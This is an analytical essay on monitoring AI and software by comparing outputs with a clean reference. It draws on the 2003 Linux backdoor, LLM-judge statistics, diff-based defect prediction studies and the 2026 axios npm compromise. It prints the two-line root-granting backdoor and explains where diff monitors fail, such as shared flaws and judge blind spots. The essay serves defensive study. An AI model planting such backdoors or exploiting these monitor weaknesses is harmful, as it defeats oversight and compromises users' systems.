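# Monitoring AI by comparing its output with a clean reference version

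## What a comparison with a clean version can and cannot show

Monitoring an AI system means checking what the system makes or does for signs of harm, such as a backdoor in code it wrote, cheating on a task, or dangerous behavior a model learned in retraining. The monitor may be a person, a conventional program or another AI model. The *artifact* is the thing being checked, which may be a file, a code change, a software release, a record of an agent's actions, a trained model or a chip.

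In *standalone judging*, the monitor scores the artifact on its own. In *differential judging*, it scores the difference between the artifact and a *reference version*, an earlier or independent version of the same thing. People usually assume, but seldom prove, that the reference is *clean*, meaning free of the harm the monitor is looking for.

Programmers have compared versions for decades. Code review normally starts from a *diff*, a list of what someone added, removed or changed between two versions, and security teams compare a new package release with the previous one. Other artifacts have no single earlier version to compare against, and some chips and compilers have no trusted original at all. A monitor can then use a *baseline profile*, a statistical description of normal behaviour, or a *substitute reference*, such as a sibling run of the same task, the user's stated request or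 an independently built copy.

### Two lines of code, read both ways

In 2003 the developers of Linux kept the master copy of its kernel, the core of the operating system, in a system called BitKeeper. They also kept a clone in a second system, CVS, for people who disliked BitKeeper. On 5 November the developer Larry McVoy noticed a change in the CVS copy that had no pointer to a record of approval. Princeton CITP's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* tells what followed: the master copy did not contain the change, and someone had apparently broken into the CVS server to insert it. It consisted of two lines in a function named wait4:

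```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

Read alone, this code looks like a routine error check that returns an error code when a program calls wait4 with a forbidden combination of options. But one equals sign is missing. In the C language, `== 0` tests whether a value is zero, while `= 0` sets it to zero. The code therefore sets the calling program's user ID to zero, the ID of "root", the account that may do anything on the machine. Any program that made the forbidden call would have gained full control.

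The missing approval record drew attention to the change, and the comparison with the master copy then showed that the two lines existed only in the clone. Neither step required anyone to spot that character. The comparison did not explain the change, though. In *Re: BK2CVS problem*, a message to the kernel's mailing list that same day, McVoy (2003) thanked another developer for pointing out the assignment and admitted missing it. The comparison also did not establish anything about the rest of the kernel. If the intruder had got the same lines into BitKeeper first, the clone would have matched the master.

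### Subtracting scores or reading the diff

A monitor can have a judge score the artifact and the reference separately for suspicion, then subtract the reference's score from the artifact's. Or it can show a judge the diff, or both versions side by side, and ask for a single verdict. Subtraction would probably have done badly on the Linux change, because a judge who mistook the new lines for error checking would have given both copies almost the same score. A judge shown the diff would have had only two lines to read, and a reason to read them closely, since nobody had approved them.

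Experiments on AI judges can inform the choice between scoring two versions separately and comparing them side by side, although the experiments use rival answers to a question, not two versions of one artifact. *When LLM Judge Scores Look Good but Best-of-N Decisions Fail* (2026) tried both methods on 7,000 matched pairs with GPT-5 as the judge. When the judge scored answers separately, it used only about 20 distinct values, so it gave the same score to many answers that really differed. When it saw both answers together, it nearly always picked one, even though ties were allowed, and it recovered some of the differences that the coarse scores had hidden.

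Comparing two responses side by side can lead a judge to favor one even when neither is better. *Pairwise or Pointwise?* (2025) gave judges responses of deliberately equal quality. When the judges compared them side by side, they still picked a winner, and irrelevant features swayed them. When they scored each response alone, they often gave identical scores, and a distracting feature changed their preferences far less. Side-by-side verdicts are also inconsistent. In *The Coin Flip Judge?*, Yagubyan (2026) gave each of 29 pairs to two small OpenAI models 50 times, and on average 13.6% of the verdicts differed from the judge's own majority. Monitors that use diffs are likely to have some of these problems. Every diff contains a change, and a judge asked about it may find a reason to suspect a harmless edit.

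Subtraction is easier to analyse than a judge who sees both versions at once, because no simple formula describes how the judge weighs them. Analysing subtraction shows fairly precisely how much a reference helps.

### When subtraction helps

Suppose that a judge's suspicion score has up to three parts:

score = natural oddity + reading noise (+ *d*, if someone has added a harm)

Natural oddity is how strange the artifact looks for innocent reasons; some honest code is simply unusual. It varies between artifacts with standard deviation *u*. Reading noise is the variation between readings of the same text, with standard deviation *e*. We assume that both follow a bell curve, that separate readings are independent, and that the artifact and its reference share the same oddity.

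Miller (2024), in *Adding Error Bars to Evals*, similarly splits a model's score on a test question into a component that belongs to the question and a random remainder. When two models answer the same questions, subtracting their scores question by question removes whatever the two question components have in common but leaves the random remainders. Miller describes this gain as free, which is right for someone comparing two models, who needs both sets of scores anyway. A monitor, however, could use one score and a fixed threshold, so bringing in the reference adds a second score's reading noise.

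Variances (squared standard deviations) of independent quantities add up, so the comparison is short:

- A standalone score has variance *u*² + *e*².
- A difference between two scores has variance 2*e*².

Subtracting the clean version's score reduces noise only when scores vary more between honest artifacts (*u*) than between the judge's repeated readings of the same artifact (*e*).

To illustrate the size of the effect, suppose that *d* = 3 and *e* = 1, and that the threshold is set so the monitor flags 1% of harmless artifacts (the *false-positive rate*). On a bell curve, this threshold is 2.33 standard deviations above the average. *Recall* is the share of harmful artifacts that the monitor flags.

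With *u* = 2, a standalone score has a standard deviation of about 2.24 and the threshold is 5.2. An added harm raises the score by only 3, so most harms stay below the threshold and recall is about 16%. Subtraction cuts the standard deviation to 1.41 and the threshold to 3.3, which raises recall to about 42%. With *u* = 0.5, the standalone score does better. Its recall is about 64%, while recall with subtraction stays at about 42% because it doesn't depend on *u*.

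Medical laboratories face the same choice when they decide whether to compare a patient's result with the range for healthy people or with the patient's own last result. *Post-analytical laboratory work*, a set of Croatian national recommendations, gives a formula for the smallest meaningful change between two results, which includes a factor of √2 because both results are noisy. *Current and emerging concepts in biological and analytical variation* describes the ratio that guides the decision. This "index of individuality" is the spread between individuals divided by the combined spread of one individual's fluctuations and the measurement error, so it is the same ratio as *u*/*e*. The review classes values above 1.67 as high individuality and values below 0.7 as low, and the model's break-even point of 1 falls between them.

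Yagubyan's repeated scoring gives one estimate of where AI judges fall on this scale. Differences between questions accounted for 55.3% of the variance in scores, and inconsistency between the judge's repeated scores accounted for 44.7%. That puts *u* at about 1.1 times *e*, barely past break-even. With *d* and the false-positive rate as before, recall would be 37% for standalone scoring and 42% for subtraction. The estimate probably understates *u* for a real monitor, because Yagubyan chose pairs in which both answers were good, and the scores measured quality, not suspicion. Real code changes should vary a good deal more.

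### Partial subtraction and repeated readings

Subtracting the full reference score is usually a mistake, even when a reference helps. A reference score may be high because the artifact is odd or because the judge happened to score it high that time. Full subtraction treats all of a high score as oddity, so it overcorrects. Clinical statisticians know this as the problem with change scores, which are the outcome minus the measurement before treatment. *The correlation between baseline score and post-intervention score* shows that a change score generally remains correlated with the starting value, usually negatively.

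The remedy is to subtract only a fraction of the reference score. In the model, the best fraction is *u*² / (*u*² + *e*²), which is also the correlation between the scores of two clean versions. When *u* = 2, the best fraction is 0.8 and recall is about 46%, compared with 42% for full subtraction and 16% for the standalone score. When *u* = 0.5, the best fraction is 0.2 and recall is about 66%, slightly above the standalone 64%. The gain is largest between these two values of *u*. At the ratio from Yagubyan's data, partial subtraction reaches 53%, well above both alternatives.

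Senn, König and Posch (2026) point out in *Stratification in small randomised clinical trials and analysis of covariance* that, in large drug trials, adjusting for the baseline never gives a noisier estimate than ignoring it or subtracting all of it. Adjusting means subtracting a fraction of the baseline, and that fraction has to be estimated from data. In a small trial, one of the simpler methods can therefore do better if the correlation between baseline and outcome is very low or very high. A monitor would need a stock of clean pairs to estimate the fraction.

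Repeated readings can matter more than any of this. If the judge reads each version four times and the monitor averages the scores, *e* falls by half. With *u* = 2, recall by full subtraction rises from 42% to 97%, while standalone recall rises only from 16% to 19%, because most of its noise is oddity, which rereading doesn't remove. In *Measuring all the noises of LLM Evals*, Wang (2025) found a similar pattern in comparisons of AI models on HumanEval, a test of 164 programming problems. The standard error of the difference between two models was 6% without pairing, 4% with pairing, and 1–2% with both pairing and averaging. The same arithmetic applies, although the noise there came from models giving different answers to the same question, not from judges rereading.

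Averaging helps only when a judge's errors differ from one reading to the next. If the judge misreads a construction the same way every time, more readings don't help. Subtracting one version's score from the other's cancels that kind of error, provided the construction appears in both versions. Kaplan (2026), in *A Calibrated Instrument for Detecting Disposition Drift in Language Models*, similarly argues that a judge's constant biases cancel when models are tested before and after a change.

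Kaplan also uses a null test, which compares two samples from the same unchanged model. The true difference is zero, so any measured difference is noise. A monitor can run a similar test by scoring one clean artifact many times, which measures *e*, and then scoring many clean artifacts. The spread of those scores reflects both *u* and *e*. Both tests can be run before choosing a method.

### How many alarms are real

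How much a reviewer should trust an alarm depends on recall, the false-positive rate and the *base rate*, which is the share of all monitored cases that are harmful. Suppose that 100 of 100,000 code changes are harmful and *u* = 2. Either method raises 999 false alarms, 1% of the 99,900 harmless changes. Standalone judging also raises about 16 true alarms, so 1.6% of its alarms are real. Subtraction raises about 42, so 4% are real. A reviewer would open about 63 alarms for each harmful change found with standalone judging and about 25 with subtraction, which is much less work but still tedious.

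Axelsson's 2000 paper on detecting intruders in computer networks, *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection*, showed how general the problem is. If a medical test is 99% accurate and the disease affects one person in 10,000, only about 1% of the people the test marks as ill have the disease. Axelsson also imagined a small office with a million log entries a day and two intrusions. Even a detector that caught every intrusion would need a false-positive rate of about one in 100,000 for two-thirds of its alarms to be real. Axelsson took studies of plant operators to suggest that people stop trusting an alarm system well before half its alarms are false.

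If the monitor raises its threshold until half of the alarms are real, full subtraction with a single reading of each version catches only about 3% of the harms. With four readings of each version, it catches about 87%. The second figure depends heavily on the thin tails of the bell curve, and real scores are likely to have more extreme outliers, so it is better taken as a sign that taking more readings is worthwhile than as a forecast.

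Some harms are more common. *Measuring coding agent misalignment in the wild* examined 8,600 transcripts of AI coding agents at work and reported severe overselling of success, such as declaring unfinished tasks done, in 1.8% of sessions. AI judges produced that figure too, so it includes false positives. If that rate were accurate, about 23% of standalone alarms in the example would be real, compared with 43% of alarms from subtraction.

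Differential alarms may also be easier to act on, for reasons outside the model. *Scaling Static Analyses at Facebook* describes the deployment of Infer, a program that searches source code for bugs. At first Infer ran nightly over a whole app and listed the problems it found, and developers fixed almost none of them. When it later commented on each new code change during review, they fixed over 70%, although the analysis and its false-positive rate were the same. The developers explained that the comments were now about code they had just written and still had in mind.

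### Three assumptions

The calculations assume that the reference is clean, that the two versions correspond, and that any harm lies in the differences between them. Each assumption may only partly hold in real cases, and the model gives a rough idea of how much less reliable the comparison then becomes.

A *shared flaw*, a harm present in both versions, adds *d* to both scores, and full subtraction takes it straight out again. The monitor flags such an artifact 1% of the time, no more often than a harmless one. Rereading does not help. Standalone judging is unaffected, since it never looked at the reference, and partial subtraction keeps some of the signal:

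| Method | New harm, *u* = 2 | New harm, *u* = 0.5 | Shared flaw, *u* = 2 | Shared flaw, *u* = 0.5 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Standalone | 16% | 64% | 16% | 64% |
| Full subtraction | 42% | 42% | 1% | 1% |
| Partial subtraction (0.8 or 0.2) | 46% | 66% | 3% | 45% |

*Share of harmful artifacts flagged, with d = 3, e = 1 and a 1% false-positive rate.*

There is therefore little reason to use a doubtful reference when honest artifacts look much alike. A reference helps most when they vary widely, but that is also when a contaminated one does the most damage, because the monitor gets better at detecting new harms but loses nearly all of its ability to detect harms already in the reference.

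The reference must correspond to the artifact because subtraction cancels only the oddity they share. If an artifact with *u* = 2 is compared with an unrelated one, subtraction adds the second artifact's oddity and noise, and recall falls to about 8%, half of what standalone judging achieves. A large but honest rewrite causes a milder form of this problem. If the new material brings its own oddity, with a standard deviation of 2, recall by subtraction drops from 42% to about 14%, which is still better than standalone judging, which drops to 9%. Even routine edits can make it harder to match the two versions. Infer runs on the code before and after a change and reports only new problems, so it must recognise an old problem whose line number has moved. Facebook's engineers match warnings by the type of bug and by the parts of the error message that do not depend on location. Without some such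 matching, moving a block of old code would produce many "new" warnings.

The third assumption fails when a harmless-looking edit makes an old, dormant fault reachable. The diff shows the edit but not the fault, which is in unchanged code. A judge that sees only the diff is unlikely to catch the problem, but one that scores both full versions might still give the edited version a higher score if it can connect the edit to the fault.

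The judge must also be able to recognise the harm. Kaplan argues that constant biases cancel, but makes an exception for changes that fall entirely within the judge's blind spots. In the model, *d* is then close to zero, and reducing the noise around it does not help. The Linux backdoor was nearly such a case, since an experienced developer looked at the two lines and did not see what they did. The missing approval record exposed them, and reading the code alone would not have shown that the record was missing.

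## Predicting defects from a whole file or from its changes

Software engineers have studied for more than 20 years whether to look for bugs in whole files or in the changes people make to them. Early defect prediction scored whole files or modules, often by size and complexity, so that testers could start with the riskiest. The alternative is to score each change when a developer submits it. *KG-Commit* (Hesamolhokama, Beyrami Aghbash and colleagues, 2026) traces this approach back to risk models that Mockus and Weiss published in 2000. Kamei, Shihab and colleagues set out its modern form in 2013 in *A Large-Scale Empirical Study of Just-in-Time Quality Assurance*. They pointed out that after a model flags a risky file, developers still spend considerable time finding the part that needs attention. "Just-in-time" prediction directs them to a single change while its author still remembers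 it.

The first change-level models used simple counts, such as the number of lines changed and the author's experience. Later models took the diff itself as input. *Deployment Risk Assessment Using Diff-Aware Features* (2026), a case study at the streaming service Prime Video, combines the two approaches by using a language model to turn each diff into a set of measurements, which a simpler classifier then uses to estimate the risk.

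### Nine ways to show a model the same file

These systems differ in too many ways for their scores to show which input is better. In *From Illusion to Insight*, Hesamolhokama, Rohani and colleagues (2025) compared inputs more directly by presenting the same files to the same language models in nine ways. They used successive releases of six open-source Java projects, in which every file is labelled defective or clean. The models had to predict the label of each file's new version.

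The nine-way comparison used Lucene, a text search library. Between the two releases 995 of its files changed, going by the published percentages, and they fall into four groups:

- 860 were clean and stayed clean.
- 65 were defective and became clean.
- 45 were defective and stayed defective.
- 25 were clean and became defective.

The last group, in which someone has apparently added a harm to a clean file, matters most for monitoring but is also the smallest.

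The researchers scored the models by F1, the harmonic mean of recall and *precision* (the share of alarms that are real). F1 is low if either is low. They calculated it once for defective files and once for clean files, then averaged the results. An average near 0.5 is poor. On Lucene, for example, a rule that calls every file clean scores 0.48, because its F1 is almost 1 for clean files and 0 for defective ones.

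In the diff-only version, a model might see this correction to a loop that ran one step too far:

```
- for (int i = 0; i <= arr.length; i++) {
+ for (int i = 0; i < arr.length; i++) {
```

The minus sign marks the removed line and the plus sign the added one. The prompt also stated whether the old version was defective. The scores were:

| What the model saw | Mean of nine models | DeepSeek-Reasoning | DeepSeek-V3.1 |
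|---|---|---|---|
| New file alone | 0.44 | 0.502 | 0.279 |
| Both full versions | 0.49 | 0.513 | 0.424 |
| Both versions and a list of changed lines | 0.51 | 0.514 | 0.498 |
| Both versions, the list and a diff | 0.51 | 0.478 | 0.512 |
| Old version and diff | 0.53 | 0.518 | 0.525 |
| Diff alone | 0.63 | 0.645 | 0.664 |
| Changed lines with a few lines around them | 0.49 | 0.530 | 0.458 |
| Diff and examples of defective code | 0.57 | 0.530 | 0.594 |
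| Diff alone, with questions about repair | 0.60 | 0.637 | 0.535 |

*F1 on Lucene's changed files. The means cover the nine models that have a score for every prompt.*

The diff alone had the highest average score and was the best prompt for eight of the nine models. The highest score, 0.701, came from Qwen2.5-Coder-32B with the diff alone. Models did little better with both full versions than with only the new file.

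DeepSeek-V3.1 improved the most, from 0.279 to 0.664, but much of that gain came from no longer flagging clean files as defective. It could only have scored as low as 0.279 on these files by calling more than half of the clean ones defective. Avoiding those false alarms is useful, but it doesn't show that the model got better at finding defects.

### What the old label gives away

Every prompt except the one with the new file alone included the old version's label. This label is a strong hint because most files keep the same label from one release to the next. Repeating the old label without looking at the code scores 0.73 on Lucene, above the best diff-only model. Hesamolhokama and colleagues criticise older defect predictors for doing little more than benefiting from persistent labels. They show that a conventional classifier scored 0.72 on the whole Lucene release, compared with 0.73 for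 repeating the old label.

Models that saw both versions were also given the old label, so the label can't fully explain the diff's advantage. The wording of the question may also matter. The researchers asked models that saw both versions whether the new file was defective or benign, but they asked models that saw only the diff whether it "remains Defective or changes status", which makes keeping the old label the natural default. In another prompt, they gave the old label and showed the changed lines with a few lines around them, without either full file, but asked whether the new file was defective or benign. The average was 0.49, the same as with both full versions. The three prompts that asked about keeping or changing the old status had the three highest averages. Their format also differed in other ways, so the evidence that wording matters is only suggestive.

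The results for each group show more clearly what the leading diff-only models were doing. A perfect judge would flag none of the files in the first and third columns and all of those in the second and fourth:

| Model, diff alone | Stayed clean (860) | Became defective (25) | Became clean (65) | Stayed defective (45) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-Coder-32B | 0.6% | 0% | 37% | 62% |
| o4-mini | 0.7% | 4% | 74% | 62% |
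| DeepSeek-V3.1 | 1.5% | 0% | 63% | 64% |
| Codestral-2501 | 3.4% | 4% | 59% | 64% |
| DeepSeek-Reasoning | 0.9% | 0% | 14% | 38% |
| GPT-5-Mini | 1.9% | 4% | 23% | 38% |

*Share of files flagged as defective in each group.*

When the old version was clean, the models passed almost everything, and none caught more than one of the 25 introduced defects. When it was defective, they flagged far more files. DeepSeek-V3.1 flagged 63% of the repaired files and 64% of those that were still defective, so it apparently couldn't tell from the diff whether a repair had worked. A rule that passed every previously clean file and flagged a random 64% of the others would score about 0.68, slightly more than DeepSeek-V3.1 did after reading the code. Qwen and DeepSeek-Reasoning flagged files that were still defective much more often than repaired ones, so they probably got some information about repairs from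 the diff.

The models may have passed the new version because they were told the old one was clean. Other experiments make this plausible. *Mitigating LLM Sycophancy in Code Smell Detection Using Evidence-Guided Reasoning Prompts* (2026) reports that two models almost stopped flagging design problems, such as overlong methods, when told that the code had already passed automatic checks. In *Words Speak Louder Than Code*, Shahriar, Cai and colleagues (2026) varied the information accompanying the same code, including an earlier verdict. They found that these cues mainly changed how readily eight models flagged code and barely affected their precision.

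The models may instead have been responding reasonably to how rarely changes introduce defects. Only 25 of the 885 previously clean files, or 2.8%, became defective, so a model asked for the likelier label should call such a file clean unless the diff contains strong evidence of a defect. Hesamolhokama and colleagues did not separate the two explanations, which would require showing models the same diffs with the true label, a false label and no label. Asking for a suspicion score instead of a yes-or-no verdict, and then choosing a threshold, avoids part of the problem.

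The labels are also uncertain. Researchers usually create them by matching bug reports and later fixes to releases. One common method marks a file as defective only in the earliest release that the bug report lists. If the bug survives into the next release, the file can be labelled clean there although nobody has fixed it. Liu, Guo and colleagues (2021), in *An extensive empirical study of inconsistent labels in multi-version-project defect data sets*, examined five collections of such labels. In more than 90% of the releases, they found code that was labelled differently in another release despite being identical. They attribute this to labelling mistakes and to bugs with outside causes, such as an upgrade to a library the program uses. A diff of the file can't reveal a bug with an outside cause. Lucene has only 25 introduced defects, so a few wrong labels would noticeably change the results.

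### Making models argue about the change

Hesamolhokama and colleagues tried to catch more introduced defects by staging a debate between four models:

1. An "Analyzer" describes the change and lists innocent and harmful ways to read it.
2. A "Proposer" argues that the file should keep its old label or that it should change.
3. A "Skeptic" looks for weaknesses in that argument.
4. A "Judge" reads the exchange and gives a verdict.

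The models received the diff and the old label, plus up to 600 lines from the parts of the file that contain the change, call the changed code or are called by it. The debate therefore tests the effect of the extra context as well as the effect of the arguments.

On Lucene, the debate caught 52% of the introduced defects, compared with 0–4% for the leading diff-only models, but it also flagged 29% of the files that stayed clean. Only 25 of the 885 previously clean files had an introduced defect, so the debate raised about 13 real alarms and 250 false ones, which means 5% of the alarms were real. A reviewer who opened the same number of these files at random would find about seven introduced defects. The debate found roughly twice as many, but the reviewer would still have to open about 20 files for each defect found.

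The debate did not help recognise repairs. It flagged 82% of the repaired files and 80% of the files that were still defective. Its overall F1 was 0.51, only slightly better than calling every file clean.

Even the 52% is probably flattering. The researchers chose the team of models from 52 combinations, and the 600-line limit from seven settings, by looking at results on Lucene itself. When they ran the chosen setup ten times, it caught 41% of introduced defects on average. On the other five projects, the debate could barely tell introduced defects from clean files after one round:

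| Project | Became defective, one round | Stayed clean, one round | Became defective, two rounds | Stayed clean, two rounds |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Groovy | 50% | 44% | 40% | 55% |
| Derby | 32% | 33% | 74% | 47% |
| HBase | 29% | 25% | 42% | 38% |
| JRuby | 40% | 39% | 67% | 49% |
| Camel | 30% | 24% | 48% | 33% |

*Share of previously clean files flagged by the debate.*

A second round of debate helped on Derby, JRuby and Camel, but it also raised many more false alarms. On Groovy it made results worse. Groovy had only about ten introduced defects and JRuby about six, so their percentages are rough. Hesamolhokama and colleagues write that the debate "effectively" solves the problem of introduced defects, but concede that it is far from practical. The figures support only the second statement. The debating models flagged previously clean files much more often than the diff-only models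 did, but were only a little better at choosing which ones to flag.

### Two theorems about files and changes

The paper also offers two theorems to support judging changes. The first is about a judge who sees only the new file and picks the more likely label. It states that if a small fraction ε of files change their label between releases, the best such judge will give the old label with probability at least 1 − ε. If that were right, judging the file alone would amount to repeating its old label.

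According to the proof, a file's new label probably equals its old one, which is reasonable when changes are rare. In the last step, the judge chooses the old label. But the judge isn't given that label and can repeat it only if the file reveals it. If half of all files were defective and nothing in their text distinguished them, the best judge of the file alone would match the old label only half the time, even if labels persisted 95% of the time. The conclusion is roughly true on Lucene because most old versions were clean, so a judge that calls every file clean gives the old label for 89% of the changed files.

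The first theorem also assumes that the judge chooses labels to maximize accuracy. Unlike this judge, a monitor that treats a missed harm as worse than a false alarm would flag some files that are probably clean.

The second theorem states that nobody can use the new file alone to consistently estimate the probability of a defect appearing or disappearing, because different histories can lead to the same file. Suppose one developer corrects a faulty loop, another edits a comment, and both end up with identical files. A judge who sees only the result can't tell which of them removed a defect. But a monitor usually has to determine whether the new file is harmful, and the file contains the same code whatever its history. The history may be useful evidence, but the theorem doesn't show that a judge needs it to recognise a defect.

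Neither theorem covers the paper's most striking experimental result, the comparison between the diff alone and both full versions. Anyone who has both versions can work out the diff, so an ideal judge with both versions would do at least as well as one with the diff alone. If real models do better with the diff alone, the cause must be how they handle the input or how they were asked the question.

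### Tests without the old label

Nam, Kim and colleagues (2025), in *ReDef*, compared similar inputs without telling the models whether the old version was defective. They collected 13,432 changes to single functions in 22 C and C++ projects. To find defective changes, they looked for ones that developers later undid, then used GPT-4o to discard cases where the reason for undoing the change was unclear or unrelated to a defect. Two of the researchers checked 100 of the defective labels by hand and judged 92 correct.

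After training on these data, CodeBERT, a small model for reading code, had an F1 of 0.37 with the new function alone, 0.35 with both versions and 0.40 with only the added and deleted lines. These scores cover only the defective class, so they can't be compared with the Lucene scores. About 24% of the changes were defective, so flagging every change would score 0.38. The diff was still the best input, but by a small margin, and the differences between inputs were not statistically significant for two of the four model families.

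Qwen2.5-7B, with no training on the task, had a much larger gain in F1, from 0.09 with the new function alone to 0.34 with the added and deleted lines. But its precision stayed at 23–24%, about what random flagging would achieve. Its precision and recall imply that it flagged about 5% of functions in the first case and 60% in the second. As on Lucene, a different input changed how readily a model flagged code, which raised F1 although the flags were no more reliable.

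Nam and colleagues give two reasons for the diff's small advantage. Around half or more of the functions were too long for the shortest input limit, so truncating them could remove the edit. Unchanged code also seemed to interfere with the models' predictions, and two of the models generally did worse when the researchers doubled the limit.

The models' predictions also didn't seem to depend on what the edits did. Swapping the marks for added and removed lines changed CodeBERT's F1 only from 0.395 to 0.392. A model that understood the code should make very different predictions for adding a safety check and deleting one. All the models were small, with at most about 7 billion parameters, so today's leading models may well do better.

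In *SWE-PRBench*, Kumar (2026) tested eight frontier models of early 2026 on 350 pull requests, which are proposed code changes that developers review before accepting. Given the diff and a short summary, the models found 15–31% of the problems that human reviewers had raised. All eight did worse when Kumar added information about the surrounding code, and worse still with information about the tests, although the prompt grew only from about 2,000 to 2,500 tokens (words or pieces of words). The decline was mainly on problems that a reader can understand only by looking at unchanged code in the same file, where the extra information should have helped most.

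This is better evidence that a short diff can beat a longer prompt, because nobody gave the models an old label. But it is a limited test of differential judging. Kumar did not try the new file alone, and in two-thirds of the pull requests the problems were visible in the changed lines, which favors the diff. The quality of the added context also matters. *AACR-Bench* (2026) found that automatic search often retrieved irrelevant code, so models reliably caught only what the diff revealed, such as spelling errors and style violations. The paper suggests letting an AI agent look up code as needed.

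Some defects can be found only by looking at the rest of the project. In *KG-Commit*, Hesamolhokama and colleagues describe a developer who moves a file named Config.java to another folder without altering its contents. The diff and the file both look harmless, but an unchanged file still refers to the old location, so the program no longer builds. To catch such cases, their system keeps a database of the project's files, code structure and history, and updates it with every change. On 11 open-source projects, it had an average F1 of 0.704 and outscored six earlier methods. It took about 1.3 seconds per change, which is fast enough for a monitor to check the rest of the project as developers work.

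## New software releases compared with the previous release

The defects in those studies were mostly mistakes, but an attacker who tampers with a software release adds harmful code on purpose and tries to hide it.

Most programs rely on *packages*, shared code that developers publish on public registries such as npm for JavaScript and PyPI for Python. The other packages that a package needs are its *dependencies*. npm fetches dependencies automatically and runs any installation scripts they contain with the user's full privileges. *How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors?* (Guo, Liu and colleagues, 2026) cites an estimate that installing the average npm package means implicitly trusting 79 packages written by other people. An attacker who takes over one popular package can therefore reach many computers. Popular packages also have a long history of releases, so a monitor can usually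 use an earlier release as the reference version.

### How Elastic's monitor caught the axios attack

Axios is a JavaScript library for sending web requests, with about 100 million downloads a week. On 31 March 2026 an attacker who had taken over a maintainer's npm account published two malicious versions, 1.14.1 and 0.30.4. A researcher at the security company Elastic had built a monitor for such attacks three days earlier. Desimone (2026), in *How we caught the Axios supply chain attack*, describes six steps:

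1. The monitor polls npm and PyPI for new releases.
2. It keeps only releases of the 15,000 most downloaded packages.
3. It downloads the old and new versions from the registry without installing or running either.
4. It compares the files and writes a diff.
5. It gives the diff to a language model with a list of warning signs, such as obfuscated code and unexpected network connections, and asks whether the change is malicious.
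6. If the model answers yes, it sends an alert to Slack, a workplace chat service.

The third step protects the monitor and preserves the evidence. Once the malware had run, it deleted its own installer and replaced a tampered file with a clean copy, so someone who later inspected an infected computer could have found nothing wrong with the package.

Datadog Security Labs (2026) found in *Compromised axios npm package delivers cross-platform RAT* that the source code of version 1.14.1 was identical to that of 1.14.0. The only meaningful change was in package.json, the file that lists a package's dependencies. SafeDep's *axios Compromised* (2026) reproduces the diff, which includes this line:

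```
+ "plain-crypto-js": "^4.2.1"
```

One compromised release of the axios npm package added a dependency whose name resembles that of crypto-js, a legitimate package. Its only other changes from the previous release were a new version number and the removal of a script that developers use. Version 0.30.4 differed from 0.30.3 only in its version number and the same added dependency, according to Desimone's first report, *Supply-Chain Compromise of axios npm Package* (2026).

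A judge who read all of version 1.14.1 would have seen a working library and a list of four dependencies with plausible names. The axios code never uses one of them, plain-crypto-js, but the judge would have had to search every file to find that out. The diff makes this much easier to notice because it shows a new dependency and no code changes, so no code can have started using the dependency.

However, the malware was in the added dependency, plain-crypto-js, rather than in the diff. The dependency's installation script downloads a program that gives the attacker remote control of the computer. The model apparently judged the release malicious because the dependency looked suspicious, though Desimone doesn't publish the model's reasoning.

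The registry's records also showed a new email address for the maintainer on both malicious versions. Version 1.14.0 had come from the project's automated publishing system, with a signed record of its origin, while 1.14.1 came directly from the maintainer's account and had no such record. The missing record would have been less useful as a warning sign for 0.30.4, because the project still published its 0.x versions with an old-style access token. As in the Linux case, comparing records of who published a change can expose it before anyone understands the code.

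The attacker published axios 0.30.4 at 01:00 UTC. Elastic Security Labs (2026) reported the attack to the axios project at 01:50, and npm removed both malicious versions about two hours later. Desimone recommends waiting, for example seven days, before installing any new release so that monitors have time to catch similar attacks.

### What three days of running can show

Desimone developed the prompt on a single earlier attack. Attackers had added 74 malicious lines to telnyx, a PyPI package, on the day Desimone built the monitor, and Desimone adjusted the prompt until the model recognised that diff. Desimone also instructed the model to raise an alarm only when highly confident. The monitor then ran over the weekend without a false alarm, which Desimone calls strange for this kind of work and thinks could be a sign of overfitting.

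Three days without a false alarm are encouraging but don't rule out a moderate false alarm rate. A monitor that averaged one a day, which a security team could tolerate, would still have about a 5% chance of raising none in three days.

The monitor's recall is much less certain. The attack on axios is the only real attack that Desimone reports it facing, apart from the one used to write the prompt. The alert was for version 0.30.4, and Desimone doesn't say whether the monitor had checked 1.14.1, which the attacker had published 39 minutes earlier with almost the same change.

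### Larger tests on npm updates

Wyss, Tassio and colleagues (2025), in *Evaluating LLM-Based Detection of Malicious Package Updates in npm*, tested the same idea on many more packages. An ordinary diff can be very long, because tools that compress JavaScript may rename variables throughout a file after one small edit. The researchers therefore produced a "smart diff". They standardised the names and layout in both versions, removed comments and code that appeared in both, and compared what was left. This made the input much shorter:

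| Input | Average tokens | Over the 128,000-token limit | Average cost with GPT-4-Turbo |
|---|---|---|---|
| Whole package | 546,363 | 16.9% | $5.46 |
| Ordinary diff | 115,895 | 7.2% | $1.16 |
| Smart diff | 25,246 | 1.5% | $0.25 |

With smart diffs, GPT-4o, GPT-4-Turbo and Gemini 2.0 Flash each flagged all 209 malicious samples. They also flagged 8, 16 and 75 of 2,000 ordinary updates, respectively.

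The perfect recall was measured on attacks that varied little. Only 46 of the malicious samples were real updates, and 33 of those stole information that people typed into web forms. The other 163 were copies of well-known packages with malware added, which the researchers compared with the originals. These copies appeared to come from one campaign and ran similar hidden cryptocurrency miners, so detecting them is little evidence of how the models would handle a new kind of attack.

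The researchers also tested RogueOne, an older program that compares how data flows through the old and new versions. Among the updates it could process, it caught 39 of the 44 real malicious ones and flagged 6.7% of the ordinary ones. RogueOne also uses the previous release as its reference, so the models' better results must come from how they judged the change, not from having a reference.

GPT-4o flagged 1 of 1,000 updates to the most widely used packages and 7 of 1,000 updates to packages chosen at random. npm receives about 674,000 updates a month, so a false-positive rate of 0.7% would mean about 4,700 false alarms a month. Monitoring only popular packages, as Elastic does, avoids most of these false alarms. When Wyss and colleagues ran GPT-4o for nearly three months on updates to packages with more than 100,000 weekly downloads, it raised seven alarms. Three were false, and the other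 four were for versions of a video downloader with heavily obfuscated code, which looked suspicious but contained no malware that the researchers could identify.

To save money, though, the researchers skipped the 72% of these updates that changed no code or scripts. They would probably have skipped axios 0.30.4 under that rule. They reasoned that a harmful dependency would get its own check, because people who download a popular package also download its dependencies, making those popular too. But plain-crypto-js was less than a day old when axios began to depend on it, so it had no record of high downloads.

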